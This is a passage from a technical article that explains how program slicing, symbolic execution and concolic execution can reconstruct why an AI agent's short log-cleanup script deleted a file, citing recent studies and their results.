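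In this system, the log program would need one capability for the log directory and another for the README. A function whose type includes no capabilities could influence the deletion only through the value it returns, so a slicer would not have to check it for hidden changes. The system would not have prevented the deletion of `worker.log`, because the agent had permission to delete logs. The guarantee also does not cover any outside program that the agent starts.

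Odersky and colleagues measured how the restrictions affected performance. On τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service conversations, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher when writing Scala than when making ordinary tool calls. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software issues, the one model they tested solved 41.7% with Scala and 43.3% without it. The compiler rejected between 0.3% and 7.9% of the programs on τ²-bench, and the models usually fixed them in one or two attempts.

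The same research group reports less encouraging results for a more ambitious design. In *LACUNA*, by Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), a program contains a placeholder that describes a task and specifies the type of result needed. When the program reaches the placeholder, a model writes code to fill it, and the compiler checks all of that code before any of it runs. Python would instead run the code line by line until something failed. In the log program, a compiler would catch the attempt to add a string to a number before the loop had deleted anything. Adding two integers cannot fail in Scala, so the slice would again exclude lines 6 and 10.

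On 392 tasks from τ²-bench, an agent using this design with DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76.0%, compared with 90.0% for ordinary tool calls. That 14-point gap is large, although Zhao and colleagues call the results "on par". A weaker model solved 29.1% with this design and 33.2% with ordinary tool calls. In the retail tasks, the compiler rejected 22.4% of the programs that DeepSeek wrote. Type checking alone probably doesn't explain the gap, since the earlier system also used it without lowering scores on this benchmark. The placeholder design also makes the model write much of its own control loop, and the researchers had switched off the models' reasoning. Neither study used the strongest models now available, which would probably make fewer type errors.

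*ETAS* (Tan, Wang et al., 2026) introduces a language in which every tool, agent and workflow declares the effects it may have. The compiler also summarises the order in which a program can request those effects. A developer could require approval before any deletion, and the compiler would either prove that the program complies or add a runtime check. The rule applies even in a dry run, where other code intercepts the deletions that the program requests. In a small test, the compiler accepted two valid programs and rejected four altered ones. Its optimisations cut the tokens that models had to read by 67.8% across 12 workflows. These results show that the checks work on simple cases, but they don't compare agents writing ETAS with agents writing Python.

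The agent's developer has to choose such a language in advance. An investigator who arrives after the deletion has to work with whatever the agent wrote, which today is usually Python or shell commands.

### Language models as slicers

A language model can also read a program and list the statements in the slice. It needs no dependence graph and can handle code that a classical tool fails to parse. *SLICEMATE* uses three agents based on GPT-4o. One proposes a slice and extends it from function to function, another checks it for irrelevant or missing statements, and the third repairs it. On the short Python programs, it found 95% of the statements in the correct slices, and 69% of its slices matched exactly. On the large programs, it found 69% of the statements, far more than Joern, but only 2% of its slices matched exactly.

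Small models trained specifically for slicing do well on programs like those they were trained on. *SLICET5* (He, Wang and Chen, 2025) trains a model on short Java programs and allows it to output only words that occur in the program being sliced. The model produced the exact slice for 91.3% of new programs from the same collection, but for only 14% of 100 longer programs from LeetCode, a programming exercise site. Its successor, described in *SLICEFORMER* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026), first learns how data moves through code by reordering statements that don't depend on each other and by filling in missing statements that set or use a given variable. It reached 92.2% on Java and 83.2% on Python, again on short programs from the collection it was trained on. GPT-5, which was only prompted, reached at most 14%.

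| Slicer | Test programs | Exact slices |
|---|---|---|
| *SLICEMATE* | Short Python | 69.3% |
| *SLICEMATE* | Large Python | 2.0% |
| *SLICET5* | Short Java, familiar collection | 91.3% |
| *SLICET5* | Longer Java, unfamiliar collection | 14.0% |
| *SLICEFORMER* | Short Python, familiar collection | 83.2% |

The scores are not directly comparable, because people marked the "correct" slices for *SLICEMATE*, while classical slicers produced them for the two trained models. A trained model with a perfect score would therefore have copied the classical tool's output, including its mistakes, which could be substantial. *SLICEMATE* tested JavaSlicer, which supplied the Java slices for both trained models, and reported that it found 83% of the statements in the hand-marked slices of short programs and 37% in large ones. Models newer than GPT-4o and GPT-5 would probably do better.

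Even with higher scores, a model could not guarantee that a statement outside the slice had no effect, which is what an investigator wants to establish. A model that finds 95% of the right statements on average could still miss any particular one. The risk grows with the length of the chain. To trace the deletion back to the README, a model must find lines 8, 4, 3 and 2. If it had a 95% chance of finding each, independently of the others, it would find all four only about 81% of the time. If it missed line 2, the investigator might never learn that the program had read the README, because the output would not show that a line was missing. Comments in the code could also mislead a model, whereas a slicer that walks a graph ignores them.

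A classical slicer is the better choice for a script as short and plain as the log program. If code has constructs the slicer can't follow, a model could suggest statements to add to the slice but should not be allowed to remove any.

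## Finding the statements that mattered in one run

The static slice of the log deletion contains line 1, which sets the limit to the user's 30 days. In the recorded run, line 4 replaced the 30 with 7 before the loop checked any logs, so the 30 did not affect what the program deleted. A dynamic slice contains only the executed statements that the criterion depended on in one recorded run, so it leaves out line 1. *Dynamic Program Slicing* (Korel and Laski, 1988) introduced the technique because people debugging a program usually need to explain one particular run rather than every possible run.

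### From the trace to the slice

A dynamic slicer works from a trace, which lists the statements in the order they ran. A line in a loop can run many times, so each entry also has a position. Suppose the first five logs in the directory are 3, 45, 2, 20 and 12 days old, and the fifth is `worker.log`. The trace up to its deletion then has 21 entries. The last two columns of the table refer to positions, not lines.

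| Position | Line | What happened | Where the values it used were last set | Test that let it run |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 1 | `days` became 30 | none | none |
| 2 | 2 | `notes` became the README's text | none | none |
| 3 | 3 | The test succeeded | 2 | none |
| 4 | 4 | `days` became 7 | none | 3 |
| 5 | 5 | `files` became the list of logs | none | none |
| 6 | 6 | `freed` became 0 | none | none |
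| 7–18 | 7–10 | The loop handled the first four logs | not shown | not shown |
| 19 | 7 | `f` became `worker.log` | 5 | 15 (line 7, fourth pass) |
| 20 | 8 | The test succeeded, since 12 > 7 | 4 and 19 | 19 |
| 21 | 9 | `delete` ran | 19 | 20 |

To fill in these columns, the slicer does two things for each entry:

1. For every value the statement used, it searches back through the trace for the last definition, which is the most recent statement that set the value. Lines 1 and 4 both set `days`, but line 4 did so later, so position 20 gets a link to position 4 and none to position 1.
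2. It links the statement to the test whose outcome let it run.

The slicer then follows dependences backward from position 21. The deletion depends on the test on line 8 and on `f`. The test on line 8 depends on line 4, which depends on the test on line 3, which depends on the text that line 2 read from the README. `f` depends on the list from line 5 and on earlier passes of line 7. The dynamic slice is therefore lines 2, 3, 4, 5, 7, 8 and 9.

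Korel and Laski wanted a slice to be a runnable program. These seven lines run and delete the same logs as the original if the README contains "retention: 7". Without that phrase, nothing would set `days`, and line 8 would fail. A dynamic slice accounts for the recorded run but may be wrong for other runs.

A trace also provides facts about which a static slicer has to make cautious assumptions. Korel and Laski treat each element of an array as a separate variable, since the run shows which element a statement used, so they don't need to prove that two index expressions can never be equal. However, no method can always find the smallest dynamic slice, just as none can always find the smallest static one.

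### Tests that could have gone the other way

Suppose the program runs on the same five logs with a README that lacks the phrase. The condition on line 3 is false, so line 4 doesn't run and the limit stays at 30. The loop deletes the 45-day-old log and keeps `worker.log`.

The slice of the deletion is lines 1, 5, 7, 8 and 9. These lines include the user's figure of 30 days but not the README, and they are a reasonable explanation of why a 45-day-old log is gone.

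The slice for `worker.log` is less satisfactory. No call deleted the log, so the criterion is the failed test on line 8 during the fifth pass, and the slice is lines 1, 5, 7 and 8. These lines show that the program compared 12 days with 30, but not that it had also checked the README, or that one phrase in that file would have led to the log's deletion. Line 3, which made that check, is not in the slice because no later statement depended on it. It set no variable, and the code under its test did not run because the test failed.

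Relevant slicing fills this gap. According to Gyimóthy, Beszédes and Forgács, in *An Efficient Relevant Slicing Method for Debugging*, a relevant slice also includes statements that did not affect the value but could have done so if they had evaluated differently. To find them, the slicer looks for potential dependences. A statement potentially depends on an earlier test if three conditions hold:

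- the statement uses a variable that nothing set between the test and the statement in this run;
- the program has another route from the test to the statement, and something on that route sets the variable;
- the opposite outcome of the test could send the program down that route.

Line 8 uses `days`, which nothing set between lines 3 and 8 in this run. Line 4 would have set it if the test on line 3 had succeeded, so the slicer adds line 3. It then adds line 2, which provided the README text that line 3 used.

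It adds the same two lines to the slice of the 45-day-old log, where they make no difference because that log was old enough for deletion under either limit. The three conditions consider which variables the other route could set, but not their values. If line 4 had set `days` to 60, the 45-day-old log would have survived a successful test, yet the dependences would have been the same. Telling these cases apart takes a second run with the test forced the other way, or symbolic execution to find the exact conditions for a deletion.

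A method that takes less computation is to start with the static slice and remove the lines that did not run. *Locating Faults with Program Slicing* (Soremekun, Kirschner and colleagues, 2021) calls the result an approximate dynamic slice. It always contains the relevant slice, which always contains the dynamic slice.

| Slice | Phrase present, `worker.log` deleted | Phrase absent, 45-day-old log deleted | Phrase absent, `worker.log` kept |
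|---|---|---|---|
| Dynamic | 2–5, 7–9 | 1, 5, 7–9 | 1, 5, 7, 8 |
| Relevant | 2–5, 7–9 | 1–3, 5, 7–9 | 1–3, 5, 7, 8 |
| Approximate dynamic | 1–5, 7–9 | 1–3, 5, 7–9 | 1–3, 5, 7, 8 |
| Static | 1–5, 7–9 | 1–5, 7–9 | 1–5, 7, 8 |

The approximation can't remove line 1 from the first column, because line 1 ran. The relevant slice does leave it out, but without the phrase in the README, the 30 on line 1 would have saved `worker.log`. Anyone who wants to know what the program would have done instead has to look beyond the relevant slice.

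Relevant slices are usually not much larger than dynamic ones. For *Reducing the Length of Dynamic and Relevant Slices by Pruning Boolean Expressions*, Hirsch and Hofer (2024) built a Python slicer that computes both. On a collection of programming assignments, the relevant slices were 11.2% larger on average, and about two thirds were identical to the dynamic slices. On a set of short classic algorithms, they were 2.4% larger. The relevant slices also ran more reliably. About 5% of the dynamic slices of the assignments hit the time limit, but none of the relevant slices did. The few extra lines seem well worth having when slicing an agent's script, especially to find out why something did not happen.

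### How much is left to read

Chen, Chen and colleagues (2014), in *Dynamic Slicing of Python Programs*, found that the average dynamic slice contained between 9.26% and 59.42% of the source code, depending on the program. The slice for the log deletion contains seven of 11 lines, or about 64%, which is slightly above that range.

Slicing saves far more reading in large programs. In *Precise Dynamic Slicing Algorithms*, Zhang, Gupta and Zhang sliced a run of the compiler gcc that executed 170,135 of the program's 585,491 instructions. The slices averaged 6,614 instructions, or about 4% of those that ran. But these slices followed only data dependences, and adding control dependences made them three to nine times as large. A data-only slice of the log deletion would contain lines 5, 7 and 9 but not the README.

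Soremekun and colleagues tested whether slices help people find mistakes, using 369 bugs in C programs. They assumed that a programmer would start where the failure appeared, read every statement one dependence away, then every statement two away, and so on. On average, this programmer would reach the faulty statement after reading 21% of the program, or about 40 lines. With the best statistical method, the programmer would read 26%, or 51 lines. Such methods rank lines by how closely their execution correlates with failure, so they need passing runs as well as failing ones. Slicing needs only one run, which is often all that exists for an agent's script.

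Soremekun and colleagues got the 21% using approximate dynamic slices, so an exact slicer might do a little better. They also left out bugs whose fix only added lines. If the agent's mistake was to omit a check for protected logs, no slice would contain that check, because it isn't in the program.

The method also helps less with very short programs. Someone who works back from line 9 of the log program along the approximate slice reads lines 7 and 8, then 1, 4 and 5, before reaching line 3. That is more than half of the program, and reading all of it would be about as quick.

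### The cost of a trace

Recording slows a program down a lot. Hirsch and Hofer found that tracing and slicing took orders of magnitude longer than running their test programs. The time and memory needed can still be small in absolute terms. The slicer Chen and colleagues built took at most about 13 seconds per program on average and used no more than 7.58 MB of extra memory.

Long runs are harder. Zhang and colleagues estimated that the full dependence graph for about 100 million executed instructions of gcc would take up five gigabytes, and their computer, which had one gigabyte of memory, usually ran out. They tried two ways around this:

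- **Merging the occurrences of each statement.** The graph becomes much smaller, but a statement in a loop then seems to depend on everything that it depended on in any pass. In the worst case, a slice grew more than 5,000-fold.
- **Searching the trace only when someone asks for a slice.** The slicer divides the trace into blocks and notes which variables and memory addresses each block set. It can then skip any block that did not set the value it is looking for, which was true of about 90% of blocks. The slices stay exact, but 25 of them for gcc took about five hours on a 2.2 GHz Pentium 4.

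Most code actions should need neither. A script that calls tools probably spends most of its time waiting for them and executes few statements of its own.

A more common difficulty is code that the recorder can't trace. If the agent had written `recent = files` and then `recent.pop()`, Python's own C code would remove a log from the list. A recorder that follows only Python statements would register the call but not the change to the list.

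*Focused Dynamic Slicing for Large Applications using an Abstract Memory-Model* (Soifer, Garbervetsky and colleagues, 2022) presents DynAbs, a slicer for C# programs that handles such calls. DynAbs records only the part of a program that the user cares about. When that part calls unrecorded code, DynAbs assumes that the call may have read and changed every object reachable from its arguments. Under this rule, `recent.pop()` might have changed the list, so it stays in the slice. `delete(f.path)` passes only a string, which Python code cannot alter, so the rule adds no dependence. But if line 9 had been `delete(f)`, the slicer would assume that the call could change `f.size`, and line 10 would depend on line 9.

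Soifer and colleagues tested this on Microsoft's C# compiler and on PowerShell, a command-line shell. DynAbs computed more than 1,300 slices, most of them in a few seconds. For comparison, they also recorded much more of each program, which usually changed the slices little or not at all and could take far longer. For one group of PowerShell tests, the average time rose from 0.8 seconds to almost 14 minutes, while the slices stayed the same size. The worst result for the lighter recording was a slice of 21 statements where three would have been enough. Assuming the worst therefore adds fewer unneeded statements to a dynamic slice than one might expect, perhaps because each call can reach only a small part of the program's data.

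Another option is to have a language model work out what the unrecorded code did. *LLM as an Execution Estimator* (Pei, Kong and colleagues, 2025) gives a model the partial trace, the relevant code and some worked examples from a tiny program that the tool writes and runs with full recording. The model then infers the hidden contents of objects and which step last changed them. On three sets of tests with 8,300 data dependences in total, it was right 80.3%, 91.1% and 98.3% of the time, compared with 39.0%, 82.0% and 59.9% for the best alternative. A trace that relies on a dependence inferred this way should label it as a guess, because about one answer in five was wrong on the hardest set.

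### Dependence without causation

Even an exact dynamic slice may include statements that made no difference. In the first run, where the README contained the phrase, the 45-day-old log has the same slice as `worker.log`, including lines 2 to 4. But the program would have deleted the 45-day-old log under the 30-day limit too.

A dependence means that a statement used a value or that a test let it run. Causation here means that the result would have been different otherwise. Researchers sometimes conflate the two. *CausalRepair* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026), for example, gives a language model a "minimal causal context" for fixing bugs, but computes it from data and control dependences. The system fixed 313 bugs in a standard collection, compared with 236 for the next best. A model repairing a program can ignore a few lines that made no difference, but an investigator who tells a user that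 the README caused a deletion needs to know that the deletion would not have happened without it.

### Deleting lines and running the program again

Observation-based slicing tests directly whether the result depends on a line being there. Binkley, Gold and colleagues, in *ORBS*, describe a slicer that does no dependence analysis at all. It follows these steps:

1. Run the original program and save the values at the criterion.
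2. Starting from the end of the program, delete one line and try to build what is left. If it doesn't build, delete the next line or two as well.
3. If it builds, run it. Accept the deletion if the values are the same as before, and otherwise put the lines back.
4. Go through the program again until no deletion succeeds.

The log program needs a stand-in for `delete` that only records the path, because otherwise every trial would delete files. Some trial versions can also delete more than the original. For example, if the slicer removes line 8, the loop deletes every log in the directory.

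The result also depends on the choice of criterion. If the slicer checked only that `worker.log` was deleted, it would accept the removal of line 8, and then of lines 1 to 4, leaving lines 5, 7 and 9. That program deletes `worker.log` along with everything else, so it's useless as an explanation. If the slicer compares the whole list of deleted paths, it has to keep line 8 and ends up with the same seven lines as the dynamic slice.

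Line 3 is in that result because deleting it alone would leave line 4 wrongly indented, and Python would refuse to run the program. A slicer that could also correct the indentation would turn line 4 into a plain `days = 7`. The program would then make the same deletions without lines 2 and 3, and the README would disappear from the explanation. Similarly, in an example by Binkley and colleagues, the slice of a C file keeps a print statement but loses the `if` that controlled it. Deleting a test that succeeded leaves the code it controlled running, whereas making the test fail would skip that code. The slice shows which lines are enough to reproduce the result, so it can leave out a test even if a different input would have changed the test's outcome.

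The method requires only a way to delete lines and run what remains, so it can slice a program made of Java, C and Python files, or one that calls libraries without source code. This is an important advantage for code written by agents, which often mixes languages.

The drawback of this method is that it needs many runs. Binkley and colleagues sliced two source files of bash, a widely used shell, totalling 10,804 lines. This took 42,793 compilations, 5,370 executions and almost six hours, and left 13% of the lines. *The Impact of Program Reduction on Automated Program Repair (2024)* reports median times of just over seven hours per slice for one Java library and just under 34 hours for another. Small programs need far fewer runs. A 48-line example took 36 executions, so an 11-line script with stand-ins for its tools should take seconds.

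The outcome can also depend on where the program runs. Binkley and Moonen (2022), in *Assessing the Impact of Execution Environment on Observation-Based Slicing*, point out that the slicer will delete the statement `a = 0` from a C program if the memory for `a` already contains zero. They sliced 69 C programs with different compilers and ways of running them. After they excluded unreliable slices, the results for the same criterion differed in about a third of comparisons. Python does not let a program read a variable that nothing has set, but in a persistent interpreter an earlier code action could have set `days` to 7. The slicer could then remove lines 1 to 4, and line 8 would use the leftover value. Each trial therefore has to start from the saved interpreter state, and the investigator has to treat the variables in it as possible causes. Binkley and Moonen's remedy is to accept a deletion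 only if it leaves the result unchanged in several environments.

### Two sufficient causes

When either of two lines would be enough, deleting them one at a time can make both look unnecessary. Suppose the README contains the phrase, but the directory has only two logs, one 45 days old and the other 2 days old. The program deletes the older log whether the limit is 7 or 30. Removing line 1 doesn't change the result because line 4 still sets the limit, and neither does removing lines 3 and 4, because line 1 has already set it. Removing all three lines leaves `days` without a value, and the program fails at line 8.

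An older method called critical slicing tests the effect of deleting each line on its own from the full program, then removes every line that seemed unnecessary. Binkley and colleagues show this failing on a program that sets `a` and `b` to 1 and divides by their sum. Either assignment can be removed on its own, but removing both makes the program divide by zero. When they applied critical slicing to 37 criteria, 26 of the slices did not compile or gave a different result.

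Their own slicer avoids this because it tests each removal on the lines left after earlier removals, but the slice then depends on the order of removal. In the two-log example, a slicer that works upward from the last line removes lines 3 and 4, then line 2, and has to keep line 1. Its slice is lines 1, 5, 7, 8 and 9, which attributes the deletion to the user's 30 days. A slicer that works downward removes line 1 first and has to keep lines 2 to 4, which attributes the deletion to the README. Both slices reproduce the deletion, but neither shows that a different slice would also reproduce it.

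The dynamic slice does not have this problem, because the trace shows that line 8 used the 7 from line 4. The slice identifies the limit that the program applied, but it doesn't show whether a different limit would have led to the same result. An investigator who needs to know both can compute the dynamic slice and then remove its lines in groups, leaving the rest of the program in place. In the two-log example, removing lines 2 to 4 leaves the user's 30-day limit in force, and the program still deletes the older log.

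## Finding the conditions that trigger the effect

Removing lines 2 to 4 and rerunning the program shows only what would have happened to one set of logs without the README. Symbolic execution can show which other logs the README could have affected, because it runs the program on symbols that stand for unknown values to find which inputs lead to a deletion.

### Running the log program on unknowns

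The log program takes no arguments, so its runs can differ only because of what its tools return: the text from `read_file` on line 2 and the list of logs from `list_files` on line 5. An investigator can treat both as symbolic inputs, which have a name but no value yet. Let R mean "the README contains the phrase", and let *a* be the age in whole days of one log in the list.

The software that runs a program in this way is a symbolic execution engine. For each variable, it keeps an expression in terms of the unknowns. It also keeps a path condition, which is the formula an input must satisfy for the program to follow a given path. On the log program, the engine works as follows:

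1. Line 1 sets `days` to 30. The path condition is still empty, since every input gets this far.
2. The test on line 3 could go either way, so the engine splits the run in two. It adds R to the path condition of one branch and "not R" to the other.
3. On the first branch, line 4 sets `days` to 7. On the second, the program skips line 4 and `days` stays at 30.
4. The loop picks up the log, and the test on line 8 splits each branch again. The first splits on whether *a* is above 7, the second on whether it is above 30.

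| Path condition | `days` at line 8 | What happens to the log | An age that fits |
|---|---|---|---|
| R and *a* > 7 | 7 | The program deletes it | 8 |
| R and *a* ≤ 7 | 7 | It survives | 7 |
| not R and *a* > 30 | 30 | The program deletes it | 31 |
| not R and *a* ≤ 30 | 30 | It survives | 30 |

The ages in the last column come from a constraint solver, a program that finds values satisfying a formula or shows that none exist. Most engines use an SMT ("satisfiability modulo theories") solver, such as Z3, which combines logic with rules for integers, arrays and text. If the solver shows that no values satisfy a path condition, the engine drops that path. For example, if line 9 came after a second test, `if f.age < 5`, a deletion would require an age both above 7 and below 5 when R is true. The solver may also stop without an answer, in which case it is unknown whether any input can follow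 the path.

Two of the four paths end in a deletion, so the program deletes the log when:

(R and *a* > 7) or (not R and *a* > 30)

*Bug Finding with Agentic Symbolic Execution* (Granberry, Ahrendt et al., 2026) explains how an engine called CrossHair executes Python code symbolically. CrossHair runs the ordinary code but passes in stand-in objects. A stand-in for an integer holds a formula instead of a number, and adding 1 to it produces a longer formula. When the code branches on a comparison, CrossHair adds the result to the path condition. It follows one path per run and records the branches taken, so that later runs take different ones.

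### When the README decides

The phrase in the README affects what happens to a log if the program would delete the log in one case, with or without the phrase, and keep it in the other. For the log program, this is true exactly when *a* is above 7 but not above 30, which covers ages 8 to 30 days. `worker.log`, at 12 days, is in that range.

Over ages 1 to 100 days, the program deletes logs of 93 ages if the phrase is present and 70 if it is absent. The difference is the 23 ages from 8 to 30. The percentage of ages affected depends on the range, since there are still only 23 such ages from 1 to 1,000, so it doesn't measure the percentage of logs affected. Of the first five logs in the recorded run, the outcome depended on the README for two, aged 20 and 12 days.

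Subtracting the totals works only because the phrase never prevents a deletion. Suppose line 4 set the limit to 60 instead of 7. The phrase would then protect logs aged 31 to 60, and the program would delete logs of 40 ages with it and 70 without it. In a program where the phrase prevented some deletions and caused an equal number of others, the totals would match even if the README changed many outcomes. It is safer to compare the two outcomes for each age and count the ages where they differ.

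A solver can also look for such an age directly. The investigator writes the deletion condition twice, once with R true and once with R false, and has the solver find an age for which the two versions give different results. If line 4 set `days` to 30, the solver would show that no such age exists, whereas a slicer would still keep the line.

The same method works for the user's 30-day threshold. Replace the 30 on line 1 with an unknown *u*, and the condition becomes (R and *a* > 7) or (not R and *a* > *u*). When the phrase is present, *u* has no effect, so no number on line 1 would have saved `worker.log`. This assumes the other ten lines stay the same, but the model might have written a different program if the user had said 90 days.

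The choice of unknowns can hide a problem. Line 3 checks whether "retention: 7" appears anywhere in the text, and "retention: 70" contains it. A README that sets a retention period of 70 days would therefore lower the limit to 7. R is true for this README as well, so the formula does not reveal the error. If the engine instead keeps the whole text as the unknown, the solver can find a README that contains "retention: 70" and still leads to the deletion of a 12-day-old log, but only if an investigator thinks to search for one.

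### Starting from the recorded run

Concolic execution, named from "concrete" and "symbolic", is symbolic execution guided by a real run. The engine runs the program on actual values and records the condition at each branch. It then negates one of these conditions, solves for a new input and runs the program again. For the log program, the first input comes from the recorded run, which had a README with the phrase and a 12-day-old log.

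| Run | Where the input came from | Input | Conditions recorded | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | The recorded run | R true, *a* = 12 | R, *a* > 7 | Deleted |
| 2 | Negating *a* > 7 from run 1 | R true, *a* = 7 | R, *a* ≤ 7 | Kept |
| 3 | Negating R from run 1 | R false, *a* = 12 | not R, *a* ≤ 30 | Kept |
| 4 | Negating *a* ≤ 30 from run 3 | R false, *a* = 31 | not R, *a* > 30 | Deleted |

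When the engine negates a condition, it keeps the earlier conditions and drops the later ones, because the program may behave differently from that point on. Run 3 requires only that R is false, so the engine can leave the age at 12. This run is probably the most useful to the investigator because it shows that the same log would have survived if the README had lacked the phrase.

The new runs need the same harmless stand-in for `delete` as observation-based slicing, plus stand-ins for `read_file` and `list_files` that return the invented inputs.

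*Hybrid Concolic Testing with Large Language Models for Guided Path Exploration* (Eslamimehr, 2026) credits the idea to DART ("directed automated random testing"), a tool from 2005. CUTE ("concolic unit testing engine"), from the same year, extended the idea to complex data structures.

Real values help when the program calls code that the engine can't analyse. Suppose the script calculated each log's age with a date library written in C. A purely symbolic engine would have no formula for the result and might have to stop. A concolic engine can continue with the 12 from the real run, but it then treats the age as a constant, so it records no condition on the age at line 8 and never tries a younger log. *Concolixir* (Chen, Hong and Yu, 2026) calls this symbolic downgrading and describes it as a recurring problem in Python, where programs constantly call libraries.

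### Why engines get stuck

Every test can double the number of paths. In an example from *Concolic Execution* (2026), a set of University of Maryland lecture slides, three tests in a row produce eight paths. Loops make this worse. With *n* logs in the directory, the log program has 2ⁿ⁺¹ paths, which is 64 for five logs and more than two million for 20.

Even very short programs can have many execution paths. In *Can Large Language Models Simulate Symbolic Execution Output Like KLEE?*, Feng, Gupta and colleagues (2025) ran KLEE, an established symbolic execution engine for C, on 100 programs that averaged about 16 lines. The average program had 25 paths, but one 15-line program had 1,002.

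If the number of logs is also unknown, there is no limit to the number of paths. Li, Meng and Duck (2025) note in *Large Language Model powered Symbolic Execution* that KLEE treats each possible number of passes through a loop as a separate path. Users can set a maximum number of passes, but the engine then misses anything that takes more passes to occur. The alternative is a loop invariant, a fact that stays true on every pass and lets the engine reason about the loop without unrolling it. No method can find suitable invariants for every loop.

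In the log program, an invariant is easy to find because nothing in the loop changes `days`. Once slicing removes the code that tracks freed space, no iteration affects the test in the next one, so a single log with an unknown age can represent every log. That is why four paths were enough above. Using one log to represent the rest would not work for a script that stopped after ten deletions, because what happened to each log would then depend on the logs before it.

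Some operations are difficult even on a single path:

- **Text.** In C, comparing two strings means comparing them character by character. Zhu, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Symbolon*, describe an image-file reader that checks for one of two valid two-letter codes. The engine splits at each place where a mismatch could occur, and most of the resulting paths lead to the same rejection.
- **Objects that refer to each other.** Bouras and Mechtaev (2026), in *Defusing Logic Bombs in Symbolic Execution with LLM-Generated Ghost Code*, give the example of a function that first checks whether four linked records form a ring. KLEE has to consider a huge number of ways in which they could be linked, and it did not get past the check in 10 minutes.
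- **Arithmetic.** Luo, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Agentic Concolic Execution*, discuss a program that counts the decimal numbers a computer can represent between two inputs. Between 1.00 and 1.00001 there are 84, so the loop runs 84 times and adds a condition each time, each of which the solver has to break down into 32 bits. A special version of KLEE that can handle such programs took more than 10 months to develop.

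An agent's script is less likely to have the second and third problems than the first. Most tools return lists of simple records, and most tests on those records probably compare whole numbers or check for a piece of text.

### What a short script makes easier

Short scripts usually have few conditions, and a solver can handle numeric comparisons very quickly. But the difficulty of solving the conditions depends more on a program's operations than on its length. To test this, Chen and colleagues wrote 22 Python functions, each 37 to 104 lines long. They measured the share of lines that the concolic engine PyCT reached, first with a solver alone and then with a language model (GPT-4o mini) suggesting extra inputs.

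| What the function does | Lines | Solver alone | With a model's suggestions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Classifies a triangle | 39 | 100% | 100% |
| Looks up a tax bracket | 37 | 100% | 100% |
| Works out a shipping rate | 56 | 100% | 87.5% |
| Checks settings in JSON | 91 | 79.2% | 86.7% |
| Decodes and classifies a message | 74 | 54.5% | 84.5% |
| Analyses a list of transactions | 72 | 46.2% | 91.5% |
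| Finds dates and addresses in free text | 80 | 31.6% | 100% |

The solver alone took about half a second on the triangle and tax functions. The functions near the bottom of the table use parsers, decoders, pattern matching and structured data. Agents write a lot of code like this because their scripts have to extract information from tool output. The log program is easier than most because its tools return ages as numbers.

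A short script can also call large outside systems, and the engine needs a model of what they might return. Granberry and colleagues studied 11 Python web applications totaling 1.16 million lines of code, most of which depend heavily on a database. CrossHair on its own could run only 4.5% of the 5,406 functions they selected. Starting up the application's framework, as a test suite would, raised this to 29.5%. They then had an AI agent write stubs, which intercept each database call and return a value. With these, CrossHair could run 81%.

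The stub's return value determines what the engine can learn. For `list_files`, there are three options:

- **A fixed list.** If the stub returns the recorded list, the program runs, but the engine can't try other ages.
- **A list with no restrictions.** The engine can try every age, including impossible ones such as −5 days.
- **A list with realistic restrictions.** The engine can try every age of zero or more, and no two logs have the same path.

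Granberry and colleagues chose the third option, and their agents took the restrictions from the rules that each database enforces on its records. An agent's tools may come with descriptions of what they return, which could serve the same purpose but are less reliable than enforced rules. Even the database stubs allowed many impossible situations. CrossHair found an apparent violation in 39.1% of the functions, but most of these were false alarms caused by the stubs. A tool that calls a language model would be harder to restrict, because it could return almost any text.

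### Engines that check a model's suggestions

Several recent engines use language models to get past these obstacles. How much an investigator can trust the results depends on how they are checked. If a model suggests a README that would lead to the deletion of a 12-day-old log, anyone can test the suggestion by running the program with that README. Confirming that no README would save a 45-day-old log requires a solver and an analysis that covers every path, because reruns can't test every possible text.

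ConcoLixir, which Chen and colleagues built on PyCT, still relies mainly on the solver to explore the program. A language model suggests inputs at the start, after the solver fails on a condition, and when the engine stops reaching new lines. The engine runs each suggested input concolically and collects its conditions, which the solver then uses to explore further. A bad suggestion wastes time but can't produce a false result.

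Average line coverage rose from 84.6% to 93.2% on the 22 purpose-built functions, from 57.0% to 72.2% on 22 functions from six open-source libraries, and from 61.7% to 78.7% on 75 functions from two others. All 1,190 test runs cost $1.63 in model fees. The suggestions worsened the results for three of the purpose-built functions, including the shipping calculator, on which the solver alone had reached every line. The engine was limited to 50 rounds, and the model's inputs changed the order in which it explored paths. For a simple script, it is probably better to run the solver first and use a model only if the solver gets stuck.

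ConcoLLMic, by Luo and colleagues, gives models a much larger role:

1. A model adds logging statements to the source code, so that a run shows which blocks of code it executed.
2. An agent reads the executed code, chooses a branch that the run did not take and describes what an input would need to reach it. The description can be a formula, a piece of code or plain English.
3. A second agent looks for such an input and can run Python or the solver Z3 to help.
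4. The system runs the program on that input and keeps it if it reaches the target or any other new code.

Because the conditions can be written in English, the agents can handle ones that are hard to express as a formula. For example, one branch of a calculator program runs only if memory allocation fails. The agent replaced the allocation function with one that failed after a set number of calls, and the branch ran. An investigator could use the same approach to find out what a script does when one of its tools fails halfway through.

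On eight C and C++ programs, ConcoLLMic covered between 115% and 233% more branches on average than four established engines. This gap is somewhat inflated because the other engines could not fully handle two of the eight programs. ConcoLLMic also found 11 previously unknown bugs, and Luo and colleagues confirmed each one by running the program. Each new input took 69 seconds and cost $0.21. One of the older engines produced inputs about 800 times faster on the calculator program, but most of them were less useful. On average, ConcoLLMic needed 31 inputs and 32 minutes to match the best older engine's coverage after 48 hours. These results used Claude 3.7 Sonnet, which is far behind current models.

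An unsuccessful search by this system proves little. Luo and colleagues examined 50 failed attempts on one program. In 36% of them, the target was impossible to reach, for example because that code was not part of the compiled program. In another 24%, the first agent had described the conditions incorrectly. In both cases the system fails to reach the target, so the outcome alone is not enough to tell them apart. Luo and colleagues say that their method cannot verify programs because a language model may give wrong answers.

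Other systems use the model to make the solver's job easier. Gordian, by Bouras and Mechtaev, has a model write helper code for calculations that the solver can't handle. In one example, a program computes the sine and cosine of an input *x* and takes a certain branch if their product is negative. An earlier test requires *x* to be at least 2 in size. Gordian works backwards:

1. It replaces the sine and cosine with two unknowns. The solver picks 10 and −1, whose product is negative, although no sine can be 10.
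2. The model's helper code searches for the *x* whose sine and cosine come closest to those values, and finds about 1.67.
3. This is too small for the earlier test, so Gordian moves to the nearest allowed value, 2.
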